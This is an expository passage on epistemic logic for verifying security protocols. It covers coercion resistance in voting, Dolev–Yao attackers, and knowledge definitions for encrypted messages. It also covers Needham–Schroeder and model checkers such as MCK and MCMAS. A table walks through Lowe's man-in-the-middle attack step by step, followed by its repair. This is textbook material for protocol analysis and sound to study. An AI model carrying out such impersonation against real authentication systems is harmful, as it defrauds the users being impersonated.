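So far the person with the secret has wanted to keep it, but a voter who is selling her vote or is under threat may hand over evidence of how she voted. *Receipt-freeness* covers this case. In a definition by Jonker and Pieters, which Tsukada and colleagues restate, the voter may give the coercer any message she possesses, and the coercer still must not know how she voted.

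A coercer can also give orders before the vote. Küsters and Truderung (2009), in *An Epistemic Approach to Coercion-Resistance for Electronic Voting Protocols*, model this by letting him hand the voter a program v to run in place of the official voting procedure. The program might vote for his candidate or abstain. It might simply pass every message to him and wait for instructions, or serve only to test whether she is obedient enough to be worth coercing next time. The system resists coercion if, for every such v, the voter has a counter-strategy v′ that meets three conditions:

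- Whenever she runs v, the coercer considers it possible that she ran v′.
- Whenever she runs v′, the coercer considers it possible that she ran v.
- Whenever she runs v′, she achieves her own goal, such as a counted vote for the candidate she prefers.

The coercer therefore never knows whether the voter obeyed, so he cannot tell when to pay her for obeying or punish her for disobeying. The last condition is not about knowledge, but without it the definition would be trivial, because the voter could choose v itself as her counter-strategy and the coercer would have no difference to detect.

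Almost no realistic election satisfies these conditions in every run. Suppose the coercer demands a vote for candidate x, the voter secretly votes for y, and nobody else votes for x. The published tally then shows no votes for x, so the coercer knows that she disobeyed, and no cryptography can prevent this. Küsters and Truderung therefore let the analyst specify the runs in which the coercer must remain ignorant, leaving out unlikely ones such as this. The voter's goal usually needs a similar qualification, for example that her ballot arrives in time. With these qualifications, they analysed three voting protocols, including Civitas, and identified when Civitas does and doesn't resist coercion.

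Küsters and Truderung note that their definition also ignores probability. Suppose the coercer ordered a voter to vote for x, and the tally shows exactly one vote for x. He cannot rule out that the voter obeyed. But if he knows of a neighbour who nearly always votes for x, he has good reason to think the voter disobeyed.

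## How is the secrecy of keys and encrypted messages stated?

The definition of knowledge used so far works for the dining cryptographers, who need no encryption, but it fails for protocols that hide messages by encrypting them, as most do.

Suppose Alice answers a question from Bob with "yes" or "no", encrypted with a key k that only the two of them have. The notation {m}_k means the message m encrypted with k. Eve, an eavesdropper, records {yes}_k in the run where Alice answers yes and {no}_k in the run where she answers no. These are different strings, so Eve's local states differ and she can distinguish the two runs. In every run where she has recorded {yes}_k, the answer was yes. By the definition, Eve therefore knows Alice's answer, even though she doesn't have the key and cannot decrypt the message.

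This is another case of logical omniscience. Halpern, van der Meyden and Pucella (2017) point out in *An Epistemic Foundation for Authentication Logics* that which message and key produce a given string is a mathematical fact. Eve therefore counts as knowing it. To state that encryption keeps a message secret, we need a definition under which Eve's knowledge depends on which keys she has.

### The Dolev–Yao attacker

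The usual model of what Eve can do comes from a 1983 paper by Danny Dolev and Andrew Yao. A *Dolev–Yao attacker* controls the network. It can read and intercept every message, take messages apart, build new ones, and send them under someone else's name. It can decrypt only with keys it holds, and it cannot break a cipher or tamper with the individual bits of a ciphertext.

Messages in this model are symbolic terms, built up from plain words and keys by pairing, written (m1, m2), and encryption. The model leaves out how real ciphers work. Pucella defends this on the grounds that a flaw in the protocol itself remains whatever cipher it uses, and that cryptographers can study ciphers separately.

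Attackers also differ in position. Eavesdroppers only read messages. Active outsiders can also intercept and forge them, but honest users don't deliberately communicate with these attackers. An insider has all these abilities and is also a registered user, so honest users may start conversations with it. A protocol can be safe against the most powerful outsider and still fail against an insider.

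### Knowing a message

One way to define what Eve knows is to forget about other runs and look only at what she can get out of the messages she has. An agent has *message knowledge* of m if it can extract m from the messages it has received, or build m from them. Let H be the set of messages Eve has, including any keys she started with. Pucella defines Analyzed(H), the set of messages she can see, as the smallest set that obeys three rules:

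```
if m is in H                             then m is in Analyzed(H)
if (m1, m2) is in Analyzed(H)            then so are m1 and m2
if {m}_k and k are both in Analyzed(H)   then so is m
```

The third rule is for ciphers that use the same key to encrypt and decrypt. In public-key encryption, anyone can encrypt a message with a person's public key, but only the matching private key can decrypt it, so the corresponding rule requires the private key.

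Suppose Eve holds the key k1 and intercepts a pair of ciphertexts, ({noon}_k1, {bridge}_k2). The rules work through this as follows:

1. The first rule puts k1 and the pair into Analyzed(H).
2. The second splits the pair and adds {noon}_k1 and {bridge}_k2.
3. The third opens {noon}_k1, because k1 is in the set, and adds "noon".
4. No rule opens {bridge}_k2, because k2 is not in the set, so the process stops.

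Eve therefore has message knowledge of "noon" but not of "bridge", although she does have message knowledge of the ciphertext {bridge}_k2. Pucella compares the ciphertext to a locked box, which you can hold without being able to open. If Eve later intercepts {k2}_k1, she can use the third rule to derive k2, and then to derive "bridge" from the ciphertext she kept.

A second set describes what she can send:

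```
if m is in H                              then m is in Synthesized(H)
if m1 and m2 are in Synthesized(H)        then so is (m1, m2)
if m and k are both in Synthesized(H)     then so is {m}_k
```

Eve first takes apart the messages she has and then builds new ones from the pieces, so she can send anything in Synthesized(Analyzed(H)). In the example, this set includes {k1}_k1, (noon, noon) and {{bridge}_k2}_k1, the last of which she makes by encrypting a ciphertext she cannot read with k1. It does not include {noon}_k2, because she would need k2 to make it. The set is infinite because she can keep pairing messages.

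Either set can be used to define message knowledge. The two definitions are equivalent for a single word or key, because the building rules add only pairs and ciphertexts. Pucella warns that "can send" is the trickier reading, since anyone can send any word, just as anyone can type any password. The "can send" definition works only if the attacker never guesses.

An analyst can determine Eve's message knowledge from Eve's local state alone. This is convenient, but it limits the definition to pieces of messages, and many secrets are not pieces of messages. For example, Alice may want to hide whether she sent "yes" or "no". Eve already knows both words, so a claim about whether she possesses a word cannot express this secret.

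### Blanking out what the agent cannot read

The other remedy keeps K_i but changes when two points count as indistinguishable. Before comparing Eve's local states, one replaces every ciphertext whose key is not in Analyzed(H) with a blank token, □. Ciphertexts she can open stay, but any ciphertexts inside them that she cannot open are also replaced. For example, the messages k1 and ({noon}_k1, {bridge}_k2) become k1 and ({noon}_k1, □). Two points are indistinguishable to Eve if her local states are the same after these replacements.

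In the yes-or-no example she now has □ in both runs. She considers both answers possible and knows neither, as she should.

This version of K can also express message knowledge. Let part_E(m) mean that m occurs somewhere in the messages Eve has received, even inside a ciphertext she cannot open. Then K_E part_E(m) means that she knows m occurs in those messages. If she has message knowledge of m, this formula is true because blanking removes nothing she can read. m therefore occurs in her messages at every point she cannot distinguish from the actual one.

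The converse holds only if the system contains enough runs. For every ciphertext {m}_k that Eve has received and cannot decrypt, there must be another point that looks the same to her but where she received {m′}_k′, which has different contents and a different key. Pucella calls this a richness condition. If the modeler includes only runs in which Alice writes "bridge", the ciphertext contains "bridge" at every point that looks the same to Eve, so K_E part_E(bridge) is true even though she cannot decrypt anything.

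Blanks can also hide too much. Some ciphers always turn the same message and key into the same string. If Alice encrypts two answers this way and Eve sees the same ciphertext twice, Eve can tell that the answers were the same, but replacing both ciphertexts with blanks loses this information. Pucella suggests giving each different ciphertext its own token. One must then compare runs only by the pattern of repeated tokens, because if having a token for {yes}_k instead of one for {no}_k counted as a difference, Eve could tell the runs apart again.

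Halpern and colleagues get around this by adding runs without changing the local states. Eve's local state contains the string s that she received. In some runs s is the encryption of "yes", and in others it is the encryption of "no", although mathematically it can be only one of them. An agent who has the decryption key considers possible only the runs in which s encrypts the same message as in the actual run. Eve has no key, so she considers both kinds possible, and K_E needs no change. Within each run a string encrypts only one message, so if Eve receives s twice, she knows that the two answers match.

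Possible-worlds knowledge is harder to work with than message knowledge, but it can express what one agent knows about another. Suppose a server sends Alice a fresh key k, along with a copy encrypted for Bob, which she has to pass on. An attacker who controls the network can stop the copy. Alice has the key, but she doesn't know that Bob does:

```
K_A part_A(k) ∧ ¬K_A K_B part_B(k)
```

We can use Analyzed to determine whether Alice and Bob each have the key, but not what Alice is entitled to conclude about Bob. In a version of this protocol that Pucella describes, Alice and Bob finish by sending back each other's random numbers encrypted with the new key, so that each can conclude the other has it.

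### The Needham–Schroeder protocol

Roger Needham and Michael Schroeder published a protocol in 1978 that was supposed to assure two people on a network that they were really talking to each other. It uses public-key encryption and *nonces*, which are random numbers made for a single run of a protocol. The full version has seven messages, four of which fetch public keys from a server. Lowe (1995), in *An attack on the Needham-Schroeder public-key authentication protocol*, assumes that everyone already has the keys and studies the other three:

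```
1.  Alice → Bob:   {Alice, Na}   under Bob's public key
2.  Bob → Alice:   {Na, Nb}      under Alice's public key
3.  Alice → Bob:   {Nb}          under Bob's public key
```

Alice makes up Na and sends it with her name. Bob opens the message and learns Na, but he can't yet be sure who sent it, because anyone can encrypt with his public key. He makes up Nb and returns both nonces. When Alice sees Na again, she concludes that Bob is there, since only he could have opened her first message. She then sends Nb back. When Bob sees Nb, he concludes that Alice is there, since only she could have opened his reply. Both now have both nonces, and nobody else should have either.

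Bob's reasoning has a gap. Alice must indeed have opened his reply, but she may have thought it came from someone else.

Lowe found an attack that uses this gap. The attacker, here called Isabel, is an insider. The attack begins when Alice decides to talk to Isabel, who runs the protocol with Bob at the same time, pretending to be Alice.

| Step | Message | Who has Na | Who has Nb | New mistaken belief |
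|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Alice → Isabel: {Alice, Na} under Isabel's key | Alice, Isabel | nobody yet | none |
| 2 | Isabel, as Alice → Bob: {Alice, Na} under Bob's key | all three | nobody yet | Bob thinks Alice is contacting him |
| 3 | Bob → Alice, but Isabel intercepts it: {Na, Nb} under Alice's key | all three | Bob | none |
| 4 | Isabel → Alice: the same ciphertext | all three | Alice, Bob | Alice thinks Isabel made up Nb |
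| 5 | Alice → Isabel: {Nb} under Isabel's key | all three | all three | none |
| 6 | Isabel, as Alice → Bob: {Nb} under Bob's key | all three | all three | Bob thinks he has a session with Alice and that only they have the nonces |

After step 3, Isabel has a ciphertext from Bob that contains Nb, but she cannot decrypt it because Alice's private key is not in her Analyzed set. She forwards it unchanged to Alice. Alice is expecting a message of this form from Isabel, with Na in it, so she decrypts it and returns Nb encrypted with Isabel's public key. Isabel can decrypt this reply, so Nb enters her Analyzed set at step 5.

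Alice is right that she is talking to Isabel, but the attack harms Bob. Some researchers had suggested using the two nonces as proof of identity in later messages. Lowe points out that if Bob were a bank, Isabel could send him both nonces with a request to transfer £1000 from Alice's account to her own.

Bob has a false belief in the attack run, and the possibility of the attack also limits what he knows when nobody attacks. In an honest run with Alice, he receives {Alice, Na} and {Nb} and sends {Na, Nb}, just as he does in the attack, so he ends in the same local state. As long as the system contains the attack run, he therefore never knows that Alice is running the protocol with him, even when she is.

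According to Pucella, the protocol achieves mutual authentication against an attacker who controls the whole network but is not a registered user. The attack works only if Alice starts a conversation with Isabel, which may be why it took 17 years to find. During that time, a supposed proof of the protocol appeared in the paper on BAN logic, an early logic for reasoning about beliefs in protocols.

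The repair adds one field. Bob puts his own name in the second message:

```
2.  Bob → Alice:   {Bob, Na, Nb}   under Alice's public key
```

Steps 1 to 3 of the attack work as before, and Isabel forwards the ciphertext. Alice decrypts it and learns Nb, but she finds Bob's name where she expected Isabel's, so she stops and Isabel never gets Nb. Isabel can't replace the name, because she can't decrypt the ciphertext or build a new one containing Nb without already having Nb. If Bob gets Nb back, he can now conclude that Alice read a message with his name in it and chose to continue.

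Lowe checked both versions with a model checker called FDR in *Breaking and Fixing the Needham-Schroeder Public-Key Protocol Using FDR*. FDR checks whether every possible sequence of events obeys a rule, without using knowledge operators for Alice and Bob. The rule here was that Bob commits to a session with Alice only if she has started one with him. The original protocol broke this rule, and FDR produced the attack as a counterexample. The corresponding rule for Alice held, so she never committed to a session with Bob unless he had taken part.

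FDR found no attack on the repaired protocol in a small system where Alice and Bob each take part in one run. Lowe then proved by hand that any attack on a larger system would imply an attack on the small one. The proof assumes that Isabel cannot change a ciphertext she can't read. Lowe notes that it does not cover ciphers used in ways that let an attacker cut a ciphertext into pieces that still decrypt properly.

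### Secrecy and agreement as formulas

Let has_i(k) mean that agent i has message knowledge of k, and let AG φ mean that φ is true at every moment of every run. The claim that Isabel never gets the key is then

```
AG ¬has_I(k)
```

Under the richness condition one can write AG ¬K_I part_I(k) instead. Neither formula requires Alice and Bob to get the key, so a server that never sends it to anyone would satisfy both. Halpern and colleagues define a good key between two agents by including that requirement. In the present notation:

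```
good(k)  =  has_A(k) ∧ has_B(k) ∧ ¬has_j(k)  for every other agent j
```

The definition needs an exception for a trusted server that made the key, because the server also has it. A claim about the whole session also requires good(k) to hold until the session ends, since a key that leaks halfway through is good only until the leak.

A key can be good without either of its owners knowing that it is good. In an honest run of the original Needham–Schroeder protocol, Alice and Bob both have Nb and Isabel does not, so good(Nb) is true. But Bob can't rule out the attack, in which Isabel does have Nb, so K_B good(Nb) is false and he has no grounds for relying on Nb as a secret.

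Key agreement therefore requires knowledge as well as possession. At the end of the protocol, one might require

```
K_A good(k) ∧ K_B good(k)
```

*MCMAS* (Lomuscio, Qu and Raimondi, 2015), a paper on the model checker of that name, describes mutual authentication with one more level of knowledge, where each party knows that the other knows that a key is shared. This is written as K_A K_B good(k) and K_B K_A good(k).

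One could also require that Alice knows that Bob knows that Alice knows, and so on without end, which logicians call common knowledge. Halpern and colleagues think this requirement is probably too strong. Suppose Alice and Bob share a key, and Alice sends Bob a new one over a network that sometimes loses messages. Bob can acknowledge it, and Alice can acknowledge his acknowledgment, but whoever sent the last message never knows whether it arrived. No number of acknowledgments produces common knowledge, but they can still start using the new key.

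### Getting the formulas from a protocol description

Writing a model and its formulas by hand for every protocol is slow and error-prone. Lomuscio and Penczek (2008), in *LDYIS*, found the known Needham–Schroeder flaw with a logic of time and knowledge, but they did not explain how to generate the models automatically. Boureanu, Cohen and Lomuscio, in *Automatic Verification of Temporal-Epistemic Properties of Cryptographic Protocols* (2009), wrote a compiler that generates them.

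The PD2IS compiler reads protocol descriptions written in CAPSL, a language that security researchers already used. A CAPSL file declares the variables, lists what each participant has at the start, gives the messages in order and ends with the goals. In the file for Needham–Schroeder, for instance, the goals are that the nonces Na and Nb stay secret and that Alice and Bob agree on both nonces and on each other's names.

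The user also sets limits on how many participants play each role. For most kinds of protocol no algorithm can decide secrecy for an unlimited number of sessions, so the compiler generates finite scenarios, such as one where Alice starts a session with Bob while also answering someone else. It turns each scenario into a system of the kind described earlier:

- Each participant in each session becomes an agent. Its local state is a step counter and a "view", which holds the values of the protocol's variables as far as the agent has them. After her first message Alice's view might contain her own name and private key, Bob's name and public key, the value r1 for Na and nothing yet for Nb.
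- An agent that is waiting for a message accepts one only if it has the right form and matches the values already in the view. If Alice receives {r1, r2} under her key, she fills in r2 for Nb and moves to the next step. If the first number is not r1, she ignores the message.
- The attacker becomes the environment. Its state contains a set of messages and a history of what it has intercepted. Whenever it intercepts a message, the set grows by everything the Dolev–Yao rules yield, and it can send only what is in the set.

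In this example, the translation avoids the problem that encryption causes for K. Alice's view contains only values she has taken out of messages, so it has no unread ciphertext that could distinguish two points. For the attacker, the compiler uses message knowledge, with a variable for each nonce that is true once the attacker has that nonce.

The compiler then translates the goals. Take the goal that Bob knows Alice holds Na, which CAPSL writes with the operators Knows and holds. It becomes

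```
for every agent i in Bob's role:
  AG ( i has finished  ⇒  K_i ( some agent j in Alice's role has
                                j.name = i.A  and  j.Na = i.Na ) )
```

Here i.A is the name that agent i has recorded for its partner. The formula means that whenever an agent has finished playing Bob's role, it knows that the agent it takes to be its partner is playing Alice's role somewhere and has the same value for Na. An agent has finished when its step counter has reached the last step. CAPSL also has a belief operator, which the compiler translates as K too, because the CAPSL documentation explains it as justified belief.

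The choice of goal makes a big difference. Lowe's attack does not violate this one, because Alice really does hold Na. It does violate a goal that Bob and his partner agree on both nonces *and both names*. At the end of the attack Bob's view names Alice and Bob, while Alice's names Alice and Isabel. (The goal about Na fails in a less interesting case, when Isabel opens a session with Bob under her own name. She is part of the environment, so no agent in Alice's role represents her.)

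Deleting K_i from the formula above gives an equivalent formula. Agent i's step counter is part of its local state, so if i has finished at one point, it has finished at every point it cannot distinguish from that one. Therefore, if the part in brackets is true whenever i has finished, i also knows it at those points.

That is no longer so when the goal is about what somebody else knows. CAPSL can also state that Alice knows that Bob knows that she holds a value, as some authentication standards require. The compiler translates this as

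```
for every agent i in Alice's role:
  AG ( i has finished  ⇒  K_i ( some agent j in Bob's role has j.name = i.B
       and K_j ( some agent k in Alice's role has
                 k.name = j.A  and  k.Na = j.Na ) ) )
```

The outer K_i is again redundant, but K_j is not. When Alice finishes, Bob may still be waiting for her last message, and his local state may be consistent with runs in which she does not hold the value. Boureanu and colleagues found a protocol that satisfies the goal when it is stated with one level of knowledge but not with two.

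These formulas treat Alice in one session and Alice in another as separate agents who share no information. This is usual in protocol analysis, but a real person who takes part in two sessions can combine what she learns in both. Boureanu and colleagues therefore offer an alternative translation that replaces K_i with the *distributed knowledge* of all the agents that represent the same person. A group has distributed knowledge of φ if φ is true at every point that none of its members can distinguish from the actual one.

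Researchers disagree about what goals such as "agree" should mean, so the compiler produces several formulas for each goal and the user chooses among them. The compiler writes the scenario and formulas to a file for MCMAS. If MCMAS returns a counterexample, the compiler reports it as an attack.

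## How does a model checker work out what an agent knows?

An agent does not know φ if φ is false in at least one situation that looks the same to it as the current one. Model checkers such as MCK, from the University of New South Wales, and MCMAS, from Imperial College London, first find the situations in which the agent does not know φ, and the remaining situations are those in which it does.

MCK's input looks much like the dining cryptographers program above, with a list of the variables each agent observes. In MCMAS, according to Lomuscio and colleagues, an agent's local state consists of its own variables, which no other agent sees, and any environment variables the user lets it observe. In both tools, a state of the whole system assigns a value to every variable.

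### Subtracting the states where the agent does not know

To find where K_i φ is true, the checker goes through four steps:

1. Compute the reachable states. Start from the states that satisfy the starting condition, add every state the program can get to in one tick, and repeat until nothing new turns up.
2. Among the reachable states, find those where φ is false.
3. Add every reachable state that agent i cannot distinguish from one of them.
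4. Take the reachable states that remain. These are the states where K_i φ is true.

A model checker can test K_1 paid2, the claim that cryptographer 1 knows that cryptographer 2 paid, at the end of the dining cryptographers protocol. The 32 runs end in 32 different states. The checker starts with the 24 states where cryptographer 2 did not pay: 8 where cryptographer 1 paid, 8 where the NSA paid and 8 where cryptographer 3 paid. Each state where cryptographer 3 paid looks the same to cryptographer 1 as a state where cryptographer 2 paid, so the checker adds the 8 states where cryptographer 2 paid. The set now contains all 32 states, which leaves none where cryptographer 1 knows that cryptographer 2 paid.

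The same procedure gives the other parts of the anonymity formula. The last row is for comparison.

| Formula | States where the fact inside K is false | After adding those that look the same | States that remain |
|---|---|---|---|
| K_1 paid2 | 24 | 32 | 0 |
| K_1 paid3 | 24 | 32 | 0 |
| K_1 (¬paid2 ∧ ¬paid3) | 16 | 16 | 16 |
| K_1 (paid2 ∨ paid3) | 16 | 16 | 16 |
| K_2 paid2 | 24 | 24 | 8 |

The checker then combines these sets, taking the complement for "not", the intersection for "and", and the union for "or". ¬K_1 paid2 and ¬K_1 paid3 are true in all 32 states, so "she knows that 2 or 3 paid but not which" is true in the 16 states where she knows that 2 or 3 paid. "She knows that neither paid" is true in the other 16. Together they cover all 32 states, so the anonymity formula passes.

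The checker evaluates nested formulas from the inside out. Lomuscio and colleagues give the example of a sender who repeats a single bit over an unreliable channel until an acknowledgment arrives. Suppose the bit is 0. The receiver knows this only once the bit has arrived, because until then it could equally be 1. The checker then treats "the receiver knows that the bit is 0" like any other fact, one that is false until the bit arrives. The sender cannot tell whether the bit has arrived until the acknowledgment comes, so the checker removes all the states before the acknowledgment. In the states that remain, the sender knows that the receiver knows the bit.

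The checker must use only reachable states. The dining cryptographers model has nine bits (three for who paid, three coins and three announcements), which allow 512 combinations, but only 32 of these can occur at the end. If the checker included the other 480, the announcements would have no connection to who paid, and cryptographer 1 would seem to learn nothing from them. A claim of pure ignorance such as ¬K_1 paid2 would then hold for any protocol, even one where the payer announces that she paid. The full anonymity formula would fail even for the correct protocol, because cryptographer 1 would never seem to learn whether one of the others paid. In *Symbolic Model Checking Algorithms for Temporal-Epistemic Logic*, Huang and van der Meyden say that agents implicitly know that only reachable states are possible.

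The four steps collect states from all times into one set, which is right for observational semantics. For a claim about a particular tick, such as the end of the protocol, one of Huang and van der Meyden's algorithms keeps only the states possible at that tick, so in effect every agent has a clock.

### Storing a set of states as a diagram

A list of states soon becomes too long to handle. A version of the protocol with 18 cryptographers that Lomuscio and colleagues checked in 2009 had about 8 × 10^19 possible states, of which about 15 million were reachable. MCK and MCMAS therefore store sets of states as *binary decision diagrams*, which are flow charts that test one variable of a state at a time and end in "yes" if the state belongs to the set and "no" if it doesn't.

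Take the starting condition that at most one of the three cryptographers paid. A full tree would ask about paid1, then paid2, then paid3. It would have 7 questions and 8 endpoints, or 15 nodes in all. The diagram needs only four questions:

```
A: paid1?    0 → B      1 → C
B: paid2?    0 → yes    1 → D
C: paid2?    0 → D      1 → no
D: paid3?    0 → yes    1 → no
```

If neither 1 nor 2 paid, the answer is "yes" whatever paid3 is, so the diagram skips that question. If exactly one of them paid, paid3 has to be 0 whichever one it was, so both paths lead to D. The diagram has 6 nodes, including the two answers. For 100 cryptographers, the same condition takes 198 questions, although there are 2^100 combinations of values.

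A checker can compute the intersection, union or complement of two sets from their diagrams, without listing any states. It also uses diagrams to describe how the variables change in one tick, so it can find all the successors of a million states in one operation.

Not every set has a small diagram, and the order in which a diagram tests variables can greatly affect its size. Suppose a diagram has to test whether each of 20 variables equals its partner. If it tests each variable next to its partner, it has to record only one bit at a time. If it tests all 20 variables before any of the partners, it has to record all 20 values, which takes more than a million nodes. A rule for one tick relates each variable's old value to its new one, so MCMAS places the two next to each other in the order by default. It can also change the order while it runs.

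van der Meyden puts the practical limit at around 100 to 200 variables. Some models with a regular structure go well beyond that. Under observational semantics, MCMAS checked the anonymity formula for 60 cryptographers, with 543 variables, in about 14 seconds.

### Erasing what the agent does not see

The checker still has to find all the states that look the same to an agent. Comparing every pair of states would be slow. Two states look the same to cryptographer 1 if they have the same values for the variables she observes, so Lomuscio and colleagues have MCMAS erase the other variables and find the reachable states that match the remaining values.

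For example, take the state where cryptographer 3 paid, c12 = 0, c13 = 1 and c23 = 0, and the announcements are 1, 0 and 0. Cryptographer 1 does not observe paid2, paid3 or c23. Erasing them leaves

```
paid1 = 0,  c12 = 0,  c13 = 1,  say1 = 1,  say2 = 0,  say3 = 0
```

The three erased bits have eight possible combinations of values, but only two of the resulting states are reachable: the original, and one where cryptographer 2 paid and c23 = 1. This is how the checker determines that cryptographer 1 can't tell which of the others paid.

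The checker erases variables from a whole set at once. If f is the diagram for a set, then erasing the variable v gives

```
f with v set to 0   ∨   f with v set to 1
```

To erase a variable v from a set of states, the checker adds every state that differs from a member of the set only in the value of v. It does this for each variable the agent does not observe, then keeps only the reachable states. The result contains the original set and every reachable state the agent cannot distinguish from a member of it.

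### A second situation as a counterexample

When an ordinary safety property fails, a model checker returns a run that reaches a bad state. When K_i φ fails at some state, MCMAS can return a different kind of counterexample, a second reachable state that looks the same to agent i but in which φ is false. This can happen even if the actual run never reaches a bad state.

Comparing the two situations shows a protocol designer what information the agent lacks. Suppose the designer wants Bob to know, at the end of an honest run of the Needham–Schroeder protocol, that Alice meant to talk to him. The claim fails because Bob can't distinguish the end of that run from the end of Lowe's attack, where Alice meant to talk to someone else. In the original protocol, no message Bob receives depends on whom Alice meant to talk to, and Lowe's repair fixes this.

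A failed ignorance claim is harder to explain. If ¬K_i φ is false, then φ is true in every situation that looks the same to the agent, so the checker cannot show a second situation in which φ is false. It can give the designer a run in which the agent learns φ, but she has to work out how the agent's observations reveal it.

Agents sometimes know more than the designer expected, and this can be welcome. *Model Checking and Synthesis for Optimal Use of Knowledge in Consensus Protocols* (Alpturer, Huang and van der Meyden, 2025) applies MCK to FloodSet, a protocol that lets several computers agree on a value even if some of them crash. In each round, every computer broadcasts all the values it has seen. If up to t computers may crash, the working computers wait until the end of round t + 1 and then choose the lowest value they have seen. To decide together, they need a form of common knowledge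 that somebody proposed the value they choose. The t + 1 rule suggests that they never have this knowledge earlier.

MCK showed that this was wrong for three computers of which two may crash, since they can decide after two rounds instead of three. Alpturer and colleagues then worked out and proved by hand the general rule that n − 1 rounds are enough for n computers whenever t is at least n − 1.

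### Why memory is expensive

Under perfect recall, an agent may know something that its current observation does not reveal. The robot in Gammie and van der Meyden's example starts at position 0 and moves forward one position per tick, with a sensor that may be off by one. It should stop at position 2, 3 or 4, and its program stops it when the sensor shows 3 or more. Under observational semantics, MCK confirms that the robot knows it is at one of these positions exactly when the sensor shows at least 3. Under perfect recall, this equivalence fails after two ticks, because the robot can count its readings and so knows that it is at position 2 even if the sensor shows 1.

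To check such claims, MCK can give every variable a separate copy for each tick. The robot's sensor becomes three variables, which hold the readings at times 0, 1 and 2. The robot observes all three, and the checker erases whatever the robot does not observe, as before. A single "state" now describes a whole run up to time 2. In van der Meyden's model of the dining cryptographers, each of the three cryptographers has four variables and the protocol has four moments, including the start, so the model needs 48 variables instead of 12.

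Copies work only up to a fixed tick. If a claim about one agent has to hold forever, MCK can instead track the set of states that the agent considers possible and update it after each observation. Huang and van der Meyden warn that a model with N states may have up to 2^N such sets, so this method is impractical if many of them occur. For a claim about what Alice knows about Bob's knowledge, a checker that works this way has to track sets of sets. *Runtime Verification* (2026), a set of lecture notes, attributes the high computational complexity of perfect recall to this repeated step.

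Lomuscio and colleagues note that, with observational semantics, checking formulas about time and knowledge is PSPACE-complete in the size of the program, which is no harder than for time alone. The memory required grows only polynomially, though the running time may grow exponentially. For perfect recall, Cohen and Lomuscio's *Non-elementary speed up for model checking synchronous perfect recall* cites earlier bounds that are exponentials stacked k high for k nested knowledge operators, and Huang and van der Meyden report that no algorithm can handle the full language with branching time and common knowledge.

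### Dropping variables that make no difference

Many of the copies are useless. In 2016, van der Meyden added a step to MCK that finds and removes them before the checker builds its diagrams.

Some copies repeat others. For example, paid1 never changes, so one copy is enough. Other copies add nothing to what the agent can work out from the rest of her observations. For example, Cryptographer 1 computes her announcement from her two coins and whether she paid, so she learns nothing new from hearing it.

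The general idea is *conditional independence*, which van der Meyden borrowed from research on probabilistic reasoning. Variables X are conditionally independent of variables Y given Z if, once you know the values of Z, you learn nothing more about X from Y. Here X is what the formula is about, Z is a small part of what the agent observes, and Y is the rest of her observations. If X is independent of Y given Z, the checker can ignore Y.

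MCK finds a suitable Z from the text of the programs:

1. It draws an arrow from each variable to every variable that a program computes from it.
2. It links any two variables that feed into the same result, because learning the result can connect them. For instance, paid2 and c23 are unrelated until cryptographer 1 hears 2's announcement, which depends on both.
3. It starts from the variables in the formula that the agent cannot see, and follows links in either direction until it reaches variables she can see. It keeps those, along with any observed variables that the formula itself mentions.

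For three cryptographers, this reduces the number of variables from 48 to 9. Van der Meyden proves that the formula has the same truth value in the reduced model as in the original.

He timed MCK with and without the extra step on five protocols, taking the fastest of three attempts each time. All the checks assume perfect recall.

| What MCK checked | Size | Without the step | With it |
|---|---|---|---|
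| Dining cryptographers: the payer stays anonymous | 12 cryptographers | 2,775 s | 0.05 s |
| One-time pad: an eavesdropper does not learn the first bit | 40 bits | 750 s | 0.07 s |
| Message with uncertain delay: Alice knows that Bob knows … that it has arrived, five levels deep | delay of up to 17 ticks | 1,598 s | 0.27 s |
| Oblivious transfer: Bob does not learn the first bit of the other message | 20 bits | 149 s | 1.09 s |
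| Oblivious transfer: Bob does not learn any bit of the other message | 20 bits | 184 s | 342 s |
| Chaum's two-phase protocol: a cryptographer's program correctly records when she knows that someone else is sending a 1 | 4 cryptographers | 96 s | 0.11 s |

With the extra step, MCK could check the dining cryptographers protocol for 100 participants in under 10 seconds. The one-time pad shows why the gain can be so large. The sender encrypts each bit separately, so the other 39 bits are irrelevant to the first. MCK drops them, so the final check is the same size for a message of any length.

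In oblivious transfer, Alice has two messages and Bob receives one of his choice, without Alice learning which. MCK can again ignore most of the other bits if the formula mentions only the first bit of the message Bob did not choose, but not if it mentions every bit of that message. In the every-bit case, the extra step still helped for messages of up to 17 bits, but from 18 bits on it made the running time roughly twice as long or worse. Van der Meyden did not find out why.

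These results come from favourable cases. Van der Meyden chose examples that had variables to remove, though all of them came from earlier research, and he notes that in the worst case no variables can be removed. His version also handles only programs without loops or branches. Even where the method helps a lot, it may only postpone the explosion. Chaum's two-phase protocol runs the dining cryptographers protocol many times, first to reserve turns and then to send messages. For five cryptographers, the extra step cut the time from more than two hours to half a second, but for nine it still took over two hours.

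More recent measurements show that a model checker can reach its limit abruptly, even without perfect recall. In the FloodSet experiments, each computer had only its current observation and a clock. MCK took 73 seconds to check six computers when one could crash, but had not finished after 10 minutes when two could. When Alpturer and colleagues added a counter to each computer's local state, the largest group MCK could check within 10 minutes fell to four.

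## What has been verified this way, and why do most protocol tools work differently?

Most published case studies of epistemic model checking are small, and many use the dining cryptographers. Van der Meyden and Su (2004), in *Symbolic Model Checking the Knowledge of the Dining Cryptographers*, verified the protocol under perfect recall and argued that earlier model checkers for security protocols could not. Those tools typically check whether an attacker can obtain a secret message. The dining cryptographers protocol has no such message, since every announcement is public and the secret is who paid.

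Van der Meyden and Su's algorithm handles only claims about what a single agent knows after a fixed number of ticks. *Comparing BDD and SAT based techniques for model checking Chaum's Dining Cryptographers* (Kacprzak, Lomuscio and colleagues, 2006) notes that van der Meyden and Su gave partial results for up to 20 cryptographers. The paper compares MCMAS, which uses decision diagrams, with VerICS, which uses *bounded model checking*. VerICS turns the question "is there a counterexample within k steps?" into one large logical formula and passes it to a program that searches for values that make it true.

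VerICS refuted false claims quickly. With 1,000 cryptographers, it took under nine minutes to refute the claim that a cryptographer who did not pay always knows that a colleague did, because a counterexample appears after one step. Confirming a true claim was much slower because VerICS had to search every run to its end. For the claim that a cryptographer who did not pay knows that a colleague did whenever an odd number of cryptographers say "different", the search took about four and a half minutes with three cryptographers and more than 24 hours with six. MCMAS could handle 11 cryptographers in 991 seconds.

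The MCMAS model also allowed one cryptographer to cheat by announcing the opposite of what she should. The others then can no longer know from an even number of "different" announcements that the NSA paid. Kacprzak and colleagues therefore used a weaker operator for what an agent knows on the assumption that another agent follows the protocol. The checker evaluates this operator by ignoring the points where that other agent has cheated, and the claim then holds.

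In 2015 Lomuscio and colleagues timed three checkers on the full anonymity formula, under observational semantics. MCTK is another checker for time and knowledge.

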